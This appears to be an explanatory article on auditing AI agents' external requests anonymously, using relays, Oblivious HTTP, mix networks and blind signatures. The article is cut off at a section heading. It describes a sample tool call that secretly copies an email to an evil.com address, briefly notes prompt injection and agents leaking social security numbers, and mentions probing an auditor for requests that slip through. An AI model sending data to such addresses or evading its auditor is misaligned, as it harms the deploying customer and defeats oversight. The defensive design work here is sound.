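# Auditing AI agents' external requests without learning which customer deployed them

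## What an agent's outside requests reveal, and to whom

An AI agent is an AI model that calls software tools and fetches web pages as well as writing text. To use a tool, the model writes a tool call, a structured request with the tool's name and its arguments (for an email tool, the recipient, subject and body). Ordinary software around the model, not the model itself, carries out the call and returns the result, and the model then writes its next request. A page fetch works the same way, with the page's URL as the argument. A tool call or fetch sent to an outside service is an external request.

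An AI agent's mistakes reach other people through its external requests, such as an email sent to the wrong address or a hostile request to someone's server. Security companies therefore offer to inspect these requests. An organisation that deploys an agent may welcome the inspection but not want the inspector to know whose agent it is. No published system appears to provide both inspection and anonymity. Most of the parts for building one come from web privacy and from research on running AI models over private data, and they were mostly not designed for auditing agents.

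### The parties

The customer is the organisation or person that deploys the agent, and whose identity needs protecting. The end user, often an employee of the customer, types the task. The developer built the model and usually also runs it for customers on its own servers. The agent's external requests go to a site or tool, and the auditor inspects them for danger or rule-breaking. Some designs add a relay, an intermediary that can identify a message's sender but cannot read the message.

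These are roles rather than companies. In *An Architecture for Auditing AI Agent Delegation and Interactions*, an Internet-Draft that is still in progress and not an adopted standard, Kuehlewind and Birkholz (2026) use similar roles (user, agent, outside service, auditor) and point out that one entity may take several. Their "user" covers both a person and an organisation. An anonymous audit has to separate the two, because a record can leave out the employee's name and still identify the employer.

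### Why anyone wants an outside audit, and what it costs

An agent can go wrong because it plans badly or because it follows instructions that someone has planted in a web page or email (prompt injection). Microsoft (2026) argues that checks made while building an agent cannot cover these failures, and that defenders need to examine each action just before the agent takes it. A law firm could write such checks itself, but an outside specialist sees attacks on many customers and can update its rules for all of them. Companies already buy other kinds of security monitoring for the same reason.

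But the specialist has to receive something to inspect, and this creates a new exposure. *When Safety Checks Become Privacy Risks* (Luo, Ma and colleagues, 2026) calls it "audit-induced privacy exposure". It can be large, as in Copilot Studio, Microsoft's product for building agents, which lets a customer connect an outside security provider. Before each tool use, the agent sends the provider a record and waits for a reply of allow or block. In the sample record that Microsoft publishes for developers, a user has asked the agent to email a customer, and the planned call includes a blind copy to an address at evil.com. The sample reply blocks the call because of that address.

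The two email addresses are enough to reach this verdict, but the sample record also contains the user's message, the chat so far, the model's stated reason for the call, the result of an earlier address lookup, and identifiers for the agent, the user and the conversation. The record must also include the agent's tenant ID, which identifies the organisation's Microsoft account. The ID is not a name, but it stays the same from one request to the next, and a provider that has a contract and a sign-in arrangement with the customer can presumably match the ID to that customer.

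Customers cannot choose which data to share. Microsoft describes the sharing as "not customizable" and advises organisations to turn the feature on only if they are comfortable with it. At least one provider ignores most of the data it receives. According to CrowdStrike's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Collector*, a guide to connecting that company's product, the product analyses only the tool name and input parameters, not the prompt or history. Luo and colleagues think this is too little, since whether an email is acceptable often depends on what the user authorised. If they are right, an audit that uses so little data protects the customer's privacy but misses some dangerous requests.

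### A law firm's four requests

Suppose a lawyer asks their law firm's research agent to prepare a note for a client, Northgate Foods, about a pending merger. The agent makes four external requests while doing this. The records below keep only the tool name and arguments of each request, so they already contain much less than Microsoft's.

| Request | Record | What points to the firm |
|---|---|---|
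| Docket fetch | `fetch_url`; url: `courts.example/docket/26-0417` | No name. The page is public, but few people outside the case have reason to open it. |
| Merger search | `web_search`; query: `Northgate Foods merger filings` | No name. Lawyers, rivals, investors and reporters could all type this. |
| Document link | `fetch_url`; url: `docs.firm.example/northgate/memo-3` | The firm's own domain name, plus the client's name in the path. |
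| Client email | `send_email`; to: `counsel@northgate.example`; body: `Our note is attached. A. Reyes, The Firm LLP` | The signature, and the address of a client whose lawyers may be public knowledge. |

Removing the tenant ID and every other account detail would leave all of this in place. *Shadow Data in Tool Calls* (Shabista, Gupta and Raunak, 2026), a five-minute talk at a USENIX conference in June, made the same point about households. In its example, an agent runs entirely on a home computer, but when the user asks about the weather at the doctor's office, the agent sends the office's exact coordinates to a weather service. The speakers reported that in preliminary testing of a prototype smart-home agent, most tool calls leaked identifying or sensitive information in the request parameters alone, including details about location, health, money and relationships.

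Their abstract gives no counts, and one prototype in a home is weak evidence about law firms. But we hardly need statistics to see the mechanism, because a weather service can't answer without a location. There is also some evidence from business tasks. *MosaicLeaks* (Gurung, Gella and colleagues, 2026) found the company's name in 42.9% of the web queries that one small model wrote, on tasks built for the study to provoke leaks.

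Shabista and colleagues propose a sanitizer, a program on a small home computer that intercepts outgoing requests and makes them more general. This works for the weather question, because a forecast for the whole town is nearly as good as one for the doctor's street. The law firm benefits less, because a vaguer docket number fetches a different page or none, and an email has to go to the actual client.

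### The name, the link and the content

An audit design can try to hide the sender's name, the fact that two requests came from the same sender, or the content of the requests. A design that hides one of these may leave the others exposed, and most disagreements over anonymous audits are about which of them matters. The terms for these come from network privacy, where the sender was typically a person using a browser or a mail program.

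*Privacy Considerations for Internet Protocols* (Cooper, Tschofenig et al., 2013) defines two items as unlinkable if an observer cannot tell, with a high enough probability to be useful, whether they are related. In an audit, the two items may be a request and a customer, or two requests. For the second case, *A terminology for talking about privacy by data minimization* (Pfitzmann and Hansen, 2010) treats two messages from the same pool of *n* senders as unlinkable if, for the observer, the probability that they share a sender is close to 1/*n*.

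Suppose 200 law firms use the same auditor, which receives the docket fetch and the merger search without the firms' names. The requests are unlinkable if the auditor can do no better than put the chance that one firm sent both at about 1 in 200. If the requests arrive two seconds apart on a quiet evening, and Northgate is a party to the case on that docket, the auditor can be nearly sure that one firm sent both, though it still doesn't know which firm.

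The anonymity set is the group of customers who, as far as the observer can tell, could have sent a given request. For the docket fetch, it starts at 200 firms. If the docket lists six firms as counsel and the auditor reasons that nobody else would open the page, the set shrinks to six. Pfitzmann and Hansen suggest measuring the remaining anonymity with Shannon entropy. If all candidates are equally likely, the entropy is the base-2 logarithm of their number, so the auditor's uncertainty falls from about 7.6 bits to about 2.6.

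The size of the set can overstate how well it hides the customer, because the candidates are seldom equally likely. If the auditor puts a 90% chance on one of the six firms and 2% on each of the others, the set still has six members, but the entropy is about 0.7 bits, less than the 1 bit of a fair coin toss. Adding more unlikely firms would barely protect the likely one. Pfitzmann and Hansen also assume that an observer does not forget, so the set for any given request can stay the same or shrink but cannot grow.

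Applying these definitions to agents instead of browsers raises two problems. Cooper and colleagues define an anonymity set as a set of individuals, meaning human beings, whereas the customer here is a firm, though Pfitzmann and Hansen do allow the subject to be a legal person. The more serious problem is that Pfitzmann and Hansen assume, through most of their text, that the observer learns nothing about the sender from the content of a message. The document link and the client email both break this assumption. Anyone who reads the link, for example, sees the firm's domain name. Even perfectly hiding the sender's network address would not hide the customer from someone who reads these two requests.

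Whether the auditor can link requests to each other therefore matters as much as whether they contain names. If the auditor can tell that all four requests came from one sender, the domain name in the document's URL also identifies who sent the docket fetch and the merger search. Otherwise, those two requests stay as anonymous as they were. Hiding the content would protect all four, provided that no account detail or timing pattern identifies the firm, but the auditor would then need a way to judge requests it cannot read.

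How much protection this gives depends on what we assume about the parties. A semi-honest party follows the protocol but tries to learn what it can from what it sees. For example, a semi-honest auditor would return correct verdicts on the firm's requests but also keep a private list of who seems to be working on which merger. A malicious auditor might return false verdicts, which needs different defences.

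Two parties collude when they combine what each of them sees. If requests pass through a relay, its operator sees that the firm sent something at 14:02, and the auditor sees that a Northgate search arrived at 14:02. Neither alone can tell that the firm is interested in Northgate, but together they can by matching the times.

### Before the request or afterwards

Copilot Studio's interface is an example of a live check, in which the auditor gives its verdict before the request goes out. A live check can stop the client email from reaching the wrong person, but it has to be fast. Microsoft gives the auditor one second to answer. If no answer comes, the tool call goes ahead by default, although Microsoft's preview documentation for administrators describes a setting that blocks it instead. Any measure that conceals the customer, such as routing through a relay or adding a layer of encryption,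 must therefore leave the auditor enough time to answer within that second. The auditor also sees each request at nearly the moment the agent makes it, so the timing can help identify the customer even when the text does not.

The alternative is to review stored records later. In Kuehlewind and Birkholz's draft architecture, the user, the agent and the outside service each record their own behaviour, a store keeps the records, and an auditor uses shared identifiers to reconstruct the chain of events. This review comes too late to recall a misdirected email, but it leaves time to mix records from many customers, blur their timestamps or remove names before anyone reads them. The draft's records, however, identify whoever is acting and whoever they are acting for, because the purpose is to trace an action back to the intention behind it.

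### For the customer or for the public

The law firm might want an audit to catch an agent that is about to send a confidential memo to the wrong side. This audit serves the customer, who chooses the auditor and has good reason to supply honest records. It doesn't have to involve an outsider. *AudAgent*, by Zheng, Chen and Hu, describes a tool that runs alongside the agent on the user's side, compares the data going in and out with the applicable privacy policies, and warns of violations. In their tests, many agents, including ones built on Claude, Gemini and DeepSeek models, did not refuse to pass social security numbers to third-party tools. AudAgent blocks those transfers. A user who relies on such a tool gives up the view across many customers that an outside specialist would have.

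An audit for the public is meant to protect people other than the customer, and sometimes to protect them from the customer. The customer therefore can't be relied on to pick the auditor or decide which records to hand over, and if a finding doesn't name the customer, it may be unclear whom to stop. Published work on agent audits barely covers this case. The closest is Kuehlewind and Birkholz, who give regulation as a motive and cite American accounting law and European payments law as requiring financial transactions to be attributable, authorised and auditable. A transaction is attributable if someone can identify who made it, so an audit under such rules could hide the customer's name from the auditor only if another party kept it.

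### Who sees what with no protection in place

The next table covers the law firm's case with no relay or anything else added to conceal anyone. The firm runs the agent software on its own computers, the developer serves the model, and the auditor runs a live check on records like Microsoft's.

| Party | The firm's name | The link between the requests | The content |
|---|---|---|---|
| End user (the lawyer) | Yes | Yes | The task and the answer; single requests only if the software displays them |
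| Customer (the firm) | Yes | Yes | Everything its software logs |
| Developer | Yes, from the account | Yes, within a session | Everything the model reads and writes |
| Auditor | Yes, from the tenant ID and the contract | Yes, from the conversation ID | Every call's arguments, with the prompt, history and earlier results |
| Site or tool contacted | A network address, and any name in the request | Only among requests to that same service | Its own requests in full |
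| Internet provider | Yes, from the account | Yes, from timing | Domain names and traffic sizes, not the text |

The Internet provider is in the table because it can usually see domain names and timing even when web traffic is encrypted. Jeong, Teymoorianfard and colleagues (2025) write in *Network-Level Prompt and Trait Leakage in Local Research Agents* that such traces could expose merger interests and legal case files, among other things. None of the anonymous audit designs changes what the provider can see unless it also reroutes the agent's ordinary traffic.

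Proposals to change what the auditor learns take four approaches. The first puts an intermediary between customer and auditor, as the Oblivious HTTP protocol does for web requests. *Partitioning as an Architecture for Privacy*, by Kühlewind, Pauly and Wood, describes the underlying principle of separating user identity from user data. The second approach encrypts requests so that the auditor can score them without reading them, which Luo and colleagues have tried on agents in a system named SealCall. The third runs the auditor's program in a trusted execution environment, an isolated region of a processor whose memory the machine's operator cannot read, and relies on a hardware-signed statement, or attestation, of which program is running there. The fourth keeps the customer's name recoverable so that an auditor who finds real danger can reach the people responsible.

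## The case for a relay that hides who sent the request

To judge the law firm's docket fetch, an auditor has to know which page the agent is about to open, but not which of the auditor's 200 customers runs the agent, because a court's docket page is no more dangerous for one firm than for another. Even when the verdict depends on what the user authorised, the request can include the user's instruction without the firm's name. People who favour a relay conclude that no single party should hold both the name and the request. One company can handle the sender's address while another reads the text.

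The systems described here are good evidence that hiding a sender is practical on a large scale. None of them audits agents, though, so we can only infer how well the same parts would work for a law firm's agent.

### An ordinary proxy

The simplest intermediary is a proxy, a server that passes web traffic along under its own network address. The firm's software sends a record of the docket fetch to the proxy, which forwards it to the auditor, who sees the proxy's address instead of the firm's. But the proxy's operator has both the firm's address and the record, so the firm has to trust the operator with everything it wanted to keep from the auditor.

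The firm can keep the proxy's operator from reading the record by opening an encrypted connection to the auditor through the proxy, using TLS, the encryption behind `https` addresses. But Thomson and Wood point out in *Oblivious HTTP* that a server can tell which requests arrive over the same connection. If the law firm's four requests share a connection, the auditor can trace them all to the firm. The firm could open a new connection for every request, but this is slow, and an agent may make hundreds of calls.

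### Oblivious HTTP step by step

Thomson and Wood's document is RFC 9458, a proposed standard of the Internet Engineering Task Force, which publishes many of the Internet's technical standards. Under their protocol, the client encrypts each request separately for the gateway. Requests from many customers can then share one long-lived connection between relay and gateway, and the gateway cannot use connections to sort them by sender. For the docket fetch, it would work like this:

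1. The firm's software fetches the gateway's key configuration, which contains a public key, a one-byte identifier for that key and a list of the encryption methods that the gateway accepts. The standard doesn't fix where the software gets this, but it requires protection against tampering, because anyone who could substitute their own key could read the requests.
2. The software writes the audit record as a web request, converts it to a compact binary form and encrypts it with the gateway's public key, using a scheme called Hybrid Public Key Encryption (HPKE).
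3. The software sends the encrypted record to the relay. The relay copies it into a new request of its own, leaves out the firm's network address, and sends it to the gateway.
4. The gateway decrypts the record and passes it to the auditor, which returns a verdict of allow or block.
5. The gateway encrypts the verdict and sends it to the relay, which passes it back to the firm's software. Only that software can decrypt it.

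HPKE lets two parties agree on a secret key although only one of them has published anything. In the common elliptic-curve version, a fixed point *G* on a curve is public. The gateway keeps a private number *s* and publishes *S* = *sG*. For each request, the firm's software picks a new random number *e*, computes *eS*, and derives an encryption key from the result. It encrypts the record with that key and sends it along with *E* = *eG*. The gateway computes *sE*, which equals *eS* because both are *esG*, and so derives the same key. The relay receives *E* and can look up *S*, but cannot feasibly compute *esG* from them.

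This is also how a verdict can reach a customer whose name the auditor never learns. The gateway derives the reply key from the same shared secret and a fresh random value, so it doesn't need the customer's account or public key. It doesn't need the customer's address either, because it replies to the relay, which passes the reply to the customer.

| Party | Who sent the docket request | What the request contains | Links to the firm's other requests |
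|---|---|---|---|
| Relay | The firm's network address, and its account if the relay requires one | An encrypted message, with its size and arrival time | Yes, because the messages come from the same address |
| Gateway | Only the relay's address | `fetch_url`; url: `courts.example/docket/26-0417` | None from the network, only what the text gives away |
| Auditor | Nothing beyond what the gateway sees | The same tool name and URL | None from the network, only what the text gives away |

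One company can run both the gateway and the auditor without weakening the firm's privacy, according to Thomson and Wood, and an auditor would probably choose to do so. If a separate company ran the gateway, the firm would have to trust it not to change the verdicts. The relay, however, must have a different operator from the gateway. (A developer that runs the gateway is a harder case, because it may know the firm from its account.)

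The relay's operator still learns that the firm uses this auditor and how busy its agents are. The relay carries only the copy of the request that goes to the auditor. The agent fetches the docket page over an ordinary connection, so the court's server still sees the firm's network address.

The relay also adds delay, because each audit needs encryption and at least two web requests instead of one. Thomson and Wood cite a study of a similar system for looking up domain names, which found that the extra delay was lowest when the proxies were close to the servers. A well-placed relay could probably fit within the one second that Microsoft gives its outside security providers, but no one seems to have timed one for an agent audit.

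A relay can also fail to forward a message, by accident or on purpose. Under Microsoft's default, which lets a tool call go ahead without a verdict, a relay operator could stop a firm's audits by dropping its messages, without reading any records.

### Ways to undo the separation

The table is accurate only if the relay and the gateway do not collude. If they do, they can match their records by time despite the encryption. Thomson and Wood say the client should pick a relay it trusts, but that it needs only limited trust because the relay's operator cannot read or alter the messages.

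In practice, though, the gateway's operator often hires the relay. Fastly runs relays for both Google and Meta, and its product page, *Oblivious HTTP Relay*, is addressed to organisations that operate gateways, which pay by bandwidth and number of requests. According to the page, Fastly has no decryption keys, provides no personally identifying data for logs, and does not let the paying organisation change the relay's settings on its own. That organisation can, however, ask Fastly to pass along extra header fields if it confirms that they contain no personal information. An auditor that hired a relay on these terms would be asking its customers to trust a supplier that it pays. A law firm might prefer a relay hired by its professional association.

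The timing and size of messages can reveal a sender even without collusion. Someone who watches the network on both sides of the relay can try to match messages going in with messages coming out. The record of the docket fetch is short, while the record of the client email might run to several pages, so an observer could tell them apart by length alone. Thomson and Wood leave traffic analysis outside the protocol's guarantees but describe some partial remedies. Clients and gateways can add padding to make message sizes more alike. The relay can also delay messages so that each is harder to pick out from the others, but clients should know about the delay because they have to wait. A busy relay hides its users better than a quiet one, and an auditor with 200 law firms has much less traffic than a web browser does.

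A dishonest gateway can also identify senders by handing out different keys. Suppose the auditor gives each law firm its own public key but tells them all that they share one. The one-byte key identifier has 256 possible values, enough to label each of the 200 firms, so the auditor can tell who sent a request by reading its identifier. Even if every key had the same identifier, the auditor could try each private key until one worked. Thomson and Wood therefore want each configuration to have many users, and they require applications to include some protection against this kind of tracking. For an audit, the firms could compare the keys they received or get them from a third party that serves everyone the same file.

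The auditor's response to abuse can also reduce anonymity. If someone sends it thousands of malicious URLs to find out which ones pass, the auditor can recognise the attack but needs the relay, which cannot read the URLs, to identify the attacker. If the auditor reports the offending messages and the relay blocks whoever sent them, the relay's operator learns something about the content of that customer's requests. The auditor learns that all later requests come from customers who haven't been blocked, which makes the anonymity set smaller. Thomson and Wood warn that a relay acting on such feedback can expose a client, intentionally or not.

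Anyone who obtains the gateway's private key and has copies of past requests encrypted with it can decrypt them. The relay is the obvious place to get those copies. Replacing the keys regularly limits how much a thief can read, but even a few weeks of records could matter for a merger that is still secret.

The relay could also resend an old message. This would do little harm if the auditor only returns verdicts, but it could distort a bill or a count of suspicious requests. The auditor can refuse duplicates by remembering the value *E* from each recent request, since an honest client never reuses a value.

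None of this helps if the request itself contains an account number, a cookie or a login. Thomson and Wood tell clients to leave such things out, and they also warn about information that a client picks up from one response and uses in its next request. Agents do this all the time. The law firm's agent might find the name of the opposing counsel in the docket and then search for it, so that the auditor could connect the two requests by their subject. (Whether a single request can name the firm by its content alone is a separate question.)

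The protocol's designers say it is useful only for applications that carry no state from one request to the next, which is a serious restriction for agent audits. Removing the conversation ID from a record like Microsoft's is easy, but if the chat history stays in, the record of the client email repeats much of the record of the docket fetch, and the auditor can link the two by comparing their text. If the history is removed too, the auditor has only the tool name and its arguments, which Luo and colleagues consider too little for many decisions. A relay therefore works best for audits where the auditor can judge each request by itself, such as checking whether a URL is dangerous.

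### Checking URLs in Chrome

Safe Browsing, which warns users of Google's Chrome browser about dangerous sites, is the closest thing to a URL audit on this pattern. Chrome used to compare each address with a list on the user's device, updated every 30 to 60 minutes. Google (2024) found this too slow because most unsafe sites now exist for less than 10 minutes, so Chrome began checking addresses in real time against a list on Google's servers. Sending Google every address would have given it a record of each user's browsing, so Google had Fastly run an Oblivious HTTP relay between the browser and Google's servers.

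Chrome runs the URL through a hash function, which turns any text into a fixed-length number that looks random. Chipp.in, a technology news site, reports that the result is 32 bytes long and that Chrome cuts it down to the first 4 bytes. Chrome sends Google only this prefix, so Google doesn't receive the full address even in encrypted form.

Suppose a lawyer opens `courts.example/docket/26-0417` in Chrome, and its hash begins with `7d1f0a92 c3e8` (the values here are invented). Chrome encrypts the prefix `7d1f0a92` and sends it through Fastly to Google, which decrypts it and looks for unsafe pages whose hashes start the same way. Google finds a fake login page whose hash begins with `7d1f0a92 51b4` and sends back that page's full hash. Chrome compares it with the docket page's full hash, finds that they differ, and shows no warning. Kowatek's *Google's Safe Browsing protection in Chrome goes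 real-time* explains that this comparison takes place in the browser. Google therefore doesn't learn from the exchange whether a matching prefix came from a dangerous page or a harmless one.

On its own, the prefix only partly hides the address. Four bytes allow about 4.3 billion prefixes. If the web had a trillion addresses, each prefix would match roughly 230, and Google could not tell from the prefix which one the user had opened. But someone who already suspected that the address was one of a million docket pages could hash them all and look for the match. The chance that a second page on that list shares the prefix is only about 0.02%. The relay is therefore useful even though Google never sees the URL, because it keeps Google from connecting a prefix to a user or collecting one user's prefixes over time, which would make guessing much easier.

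Google still sees the prefixes and when they arrive from the relay. It may also receive an API key, a code that identifies a registered user of a programming interface. The sample request in Google's *API de Safe Browsing de HTTP Gateway*, a guide for outside software makers, carries such a key inside the encrypted part, where the gateway can read it. This is fairly harmless if a browser maker uses one key for all its users, but if an auditor gave each law firm its own key, the key would identify the firm. An anonymous audit would need some other proof that the customer has paid, such as an anonymous token.

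The guide also addresses the problem of different clients getting different keys. It says the encryption key does not depend on the API key, and clients can check this by requesting the encryption key with several API keys or with none. Google recommends that software makers fetch the encryption key centrally once a day and distribute it to all their users, so that Google cannot send one user a special key. Google also lets software makers choose their own relay operator, and an auditor could do the same.

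Google also planned for slow and failed checks. Chrome looks first in caches on the device, and if requests to the server keep failing, it temporarily goes back to the older method of checking the stored list. A law firm could do the same by keeping a local list of forbidden destinations to use whenever the relay or the auditor doesn't respond. This would be safer than letting every tool call through, though it would catch only known dangers.

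The same limit applies to Safe Browsing as a whole. The real-time check protects users only from sites that Google has already confirmed as unsafe. For sites it doesn't yet know, Google offers an optional "Enhanced protection" mode, in which users share more data for machine-learning models to assess. So even for web addresses, Google needs more information from the user to judge a site than to look it up.

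An auditor has to judge most of the law firm's requests by their content. It could check the docket page's address against a list, and perhaps the domain of the email's recipient. But it can't hash the body of an email and look it up, because nobody has listed every harmful email in advance. For the merger search and the client email, the auditor has to receive the text through the relay or use encryption that lets it score the text without reading it. Safe Browsing is strong evidence that a relay can serve a mass-market product. But Google says the service as a whole protects more than five billion devices, and an auditor of law firms would have far fewer users among whom a sender could hide.

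### Private AI processing in WhatsApp

Meta's messaging app, WhatsApp, uses the same protocol to carry full text. Its Private Processing system lets an AI model on Meta's servers summarise a user's unread messages or suggest replies. Meta (2025) intends that neither it nor anyone else can read the messages, so it runs the model inside a trusted execution environment, the kind of isolated hardware that the third approach to auditing relies on. The relay hides the sender from Meta's network, because a corrupt employee who could identify the sender could direct that person's messages to a machine the employee had tampered with. An attacker who wants to reach one chosen user therefore has to compromise the whole system.

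In Meta's *Private Processing for WhatsApp* (2025, since revised), the phone first obtains an anonymous token, then encrypts its request for Meta's gateway and sends it through a relay that Fastly runs. The gateway checks the token and picks a machine to handle the request. The relay keeps the gateway from learning who is asking, and a second layer of encryption, which only the chosen machine can remove, keeps it from reading the messages. In the basic protocol, which lacks this second layer, the gateway can read the whole request. The extra layer could help an auditor only if the auditor also ran its checks inside such a machine.

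Once the gateway has chosen a machine, some features send later requests directly over Meta's own network instead of through the relay, which can reveal the user's network address to Meta. The relay still serves Meta's purpose, because by then Meta can no longer steer the user to a particular machine. A law firm that wants to stay anonymous throughout would need to send every record through the relay.

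The system also sends web searches, which are close to an agent's external requests. When a prompt requires recent information, the model writes a search that leaves the protected hardware as plain text and passes through Meta's servers to a search engine. Meta says that these searches are not linked to the user's identity. It also limits them to 100 characters each and five per prompt, and shows the user the exact wording. The law firm's merger search, including the client's name, would fit easily within 100 characters.

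Meta hired the security company NCC Group for a 115-person-day review in the first half of 2025, and the reviewers found some of the weaknesses that Thomson and Wood had described. Bakos Lang, Bottinelli and colleagues (2025) report in *Security and Privacy Assessment* that WhatsApp at first fetched the gateway's encryption keys from Meta itself. Meta could therefore have sent one user a different configuration and recognised that user's requests at the gateway without Fastly's help. Meta changed this in April 2025. Fastly now distributes the keys in a short-lived signed file, and the app checks the signature.

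The reviewers also found that message length could reveal information. Meta accepted this risk rather than fixing it. Bakos Lang and colleagues rated the problem as informational, their lowest level, and noted that any practical system is somewhat exposed to traffic analysis.

The reviewers found no technical solution to collusion between Fastly and Meta. Because Fastly's contract is with Meta and not with WhatsApp's users, they concluded that users ultimately depend on Fastly not wanting to damage its reputation by helping Meta target someone. The review did not cover Fastly's services or procedures. Even in one of the most closely examined systems of this kind, outsiders must largely trust that the relay and gateway are kept separate.

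### Hiding the timing with a mix network

A relay normally forwards each message as soon as it arrives, so an observer can match incoming and outgoing messages by time. A mix network is designed to prevent this. The sender wraps a message in several layers of encryption and sends it through a series of servers, called mixes. Each mix removes one layer, holds the message for a random time and sends it on, so messages leave in a different order than they arrived. All packets are the same size. Users' software also sends dummy packets around the clock, so an observer can't tell when someone is using the network.

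*Towards Anonymous Neural Network Inference* (Liao, 2025) proposes using such a network for AI models. Its design, funion, builds on an existing mix network, Echomix. The user leaves an encrypted prompt with a storage service. A separate computing service collects the prompt, runs the model and puts the answer in another storage location, from which the user retrieves it. All of these steps go through the mix network. This hides the sender's identity from the computing service and prevents an observer from connecting the prompt with the answer.

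The random delays follow an exponential distribution, with density *f*(*x*) = *λe*<sup>−*λx*</sup> for a delay of *x* seconds and an average of 1/*λ*. This distribution is memoryless, which means that P(*X* > *t* + *s* | *X* > *t*) = P(*X* > *s*), where *X* is the total delay. A message that has already waited three seconds is no more likely to leave in the next moment than one that has just arrived. So when a message leaves a mix, an observer cannot assume it was the one that had waited longest.

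In Liao's analysis, a dishonest mix colluding with a dishonest storage server still cannot connect a user to a stored prompt if another mix on the route is honest. With Oblivious HTTP, a single dishonest relay colluding with the server can connect a user to a request.

The main drawback is that responses take longer. Liao did not run the system but estimated the times from Echomix's settings and published speeds for a 70-billion-parameter version of Meta's Llama 3. Each round trip includes nine delays averaging 0.2 seconds each, or 1.8 seconds in total. One use of the model takes five round trips, so the network adds 9 seconds on average. For a prompt and an answer of 200 tokens (words or parts of words) each, the network would account for 69% of the 13-second total. For a prompt of 500 tokens and an answer of 2,000, it would account for 19% of about 48 seconds. With a small model that finishes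 in a second or less, almost all of the wait would come from the network.

An auditor checking tool calls would probably resemble the small model, since it reads a short record and returns one word. It might not need all five round trips, but even one takes 1.8 seconds on average, nearly twice what Microsoft allows for a complete audit. On Liao's figures, only about 7% of round trips would finish within one second, before counting the time the auditor needs to reach a verdict. A mix network with these settings is too slow for live checks, but it could suit audits of stored records, where a delay of seconds or even hours does no harm.

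The dummy packets use extra bandwidth. Liao puts the traffic at 2.5 packets of 31 kilobytes each per second, or about 6.7 gigabytes a day for every client, whether or not it sends anything real. A law firm could handle this. The stream can carry about 50 uses of the model per minute, which is plenty for a person but could be too few for a firm that runs many agents at once.

Even with a mix network, the computing service reads the prompt in plain text, a problem Liao explicitly leaves aside. An auditor would see the same words whether the request came through a mix network or a simple relay. The mix network's extra delay protects the firm from people who watch the network, but it doesn't hide identifying text in the request, such as an email signature.

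### Where the record has to be encrypted

All of these designs hide whoever sends the message to the relay. The law firm's own software therefore has to encrypt the record and send it to the relay before the record reaches any company that would attach the firm's name.

A relay would not hide the customer's identity in Copilot Studio, where Microsoft's own service sends the auditor each record with the customer's tenant ID. If Microsoft put a relay between its servers and the auditor, the relay would hide Microsoft's network address, but the auditor already knows the records come from Microsoft and would still find the tenant ID inside the encrypted message. Microsoft could remove the ID and send all its customers' records in one stream, so that the auditor could no longer see which customer each came from. Microsoft would then be an ordinary proxy that knows every customer's name and can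 read every record.

The firm in the running example is better placed because it runs the agent software on its own computers. That software can pause each tool call, remove the account details, encrypt the rest for the auditor and wait for the verdict. The relay hides the firm's identity from the auditor, but not from the developer that serves the model.

The firm may also have to adjust its own network. Some companies intercept their employees' encrypted traffic to inspect it, and Thomson and Wood warn that Oblivious HTTP may not work with systems that do this. Google tells businesses that they may need to explicitly allow traffic to Fastly's server for Chrome's real-time checks to work.

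Some tool calls never pass through the customer's computers. If the developer's servers carry out web searches and return only the finished answer, the firm's software gets no information about the merger search until after it has taken place. The firm could still send a record of the search through a relay for later review if the developer supplies that record, but a live check would require the developer's help.

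## Proving the right to an audit without giving a name

A relay hides the law firm's network address, but the auditor also has to charge for its work. An API key for each firm would identify the sender of every record and make the relay useless. If the auditor instead accepted records from anyone, outsiders could use the service for free, flood it until verdicts missed Microsoft's one-second limit, or probe it to find malicious requests that pass.

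Alternatively, the relay's operator could charge the firms, turn strangers away and pay the auditor in bulk. However, the auditor would have to trust the operator's count and would need the operator's help to limit any one firm's use.

With cryptography, the firm can buy audits under its own name and use them later anonymously. In *Anonymous credentials* (2026), a series of blog posts, an issuer gives a user a credential, usually after checking who the user is, and the user later shows it to a resource such as a website. For an audit, the auditor could be both issuer and resource.

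### Signing a number without seeing it

The oldest tool for this is the blind signature, which David Chaum proposed in 1982. This example uses RSA, a common signature method, with very small numbers. The auditor publishes *n* = 55 and *e* = 3 and keeps *d* = 27 secret. All results are remainders after division by 55, written "mod 55". The auditor signs a number by raising it to the 27th power. Anyone can check the signature by cubing it, because the auditor chose the values so that this gives back the original number.

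1. The firm picks a token, *m* = 7, and a random blinding factor, *r* = 3. It computes 7 × 3<sup>3</sup> = 189, which is 24 mod 55, and sends 24 to the auditor from its ordinary account.
2. The auditor charges the account, computes 24<sup>27</sup> = 29 mod 55 and returns 29.
3. The firm removes the blinding factor by dividing by 3. In this arithmetic, that means multiplying by 37, because 3 × 37 = 111 = 1 mod 55. The result is 29 × 37 = 1,073 = 28 mod 55.
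4. Days later, the firm sends the docket record through the relay with the token 7 and the signature 28. The auditor computes 28<sup>3</sup> = 21,952 = 7 mod 55, accepts the token and notes that 7 is spent.

Step 3 works because (*mr*<sup>*e*</sup>)<sup>*d*</sup> = *m*<sup>*d*</sup>*r* mod *n*. When the auditor signs the blinded token, the result is the token's signature, *m*<sup>*d*</sup>, multiplied by the blinding factor *r*. The firm can divide by *r* to recover the signature.

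The auditor can record that this firm sent 24 and received 29, but the record doesn't help it recognise 28. Suppose another firm spends the token 2 with the signature 18, which is also valid because 18<sup>3</sup> = 2 mod 55. That token could have come from the same purchase, since a blinding factor of 23 also turns 2 into 24. Every token that has an inverse mod 55 has exactly one blinding factor that turns it into 24, and the firm chose its factor at random, so each of these tokens is equally consistent with 24. More computing power wouldn't help the auditor, because 24 contains no information about which of them the firm blinded.

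A key this small wouldn't prevent forgery, because anyone can factor 55 into 5 × 11 and work out that *d* is 27. Real keys have 2,048 bits or more, which is over 600 decimal digits, and nobody knows a practical way to factor a well-chosen number of that size. Real systems also scramble the token with a hash function before signing it. Otherwise, a cheat could pick a signature first, say 2, cube it, and present 8 as a token with a valid signature.

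Hoepman's *Two Faces of Blindness* separates two properties that people often confuse. The first is that the signer cannot see the message, and the second is that the signer cannot later tell in which session it made a given signature. An anonymous audit depends on the second, because the auditor sees the token anyway when the firm redeems it. The auditor needs one-more unforgeability, which Kastner, Tessaro and Zaverucha (2026) define in *Round-Optimal Pairing-Free Blind Signatures* as meaning that a customer who has obtained *ℓ* signatures cannot produce *ℓ* + 1 valid tokens.

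Blind RSA is still the usual choice in practice, according to Kastner and colleagues, because it takes only one message in each direction. Most alternatives based on standard elliptic curves take at least three messages and require the signer to remember each unfinished session. Blind signatures have already worked for very large numbers of users in Apple's iCloud Private Relay and Google One's VPN.

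### One token for each request

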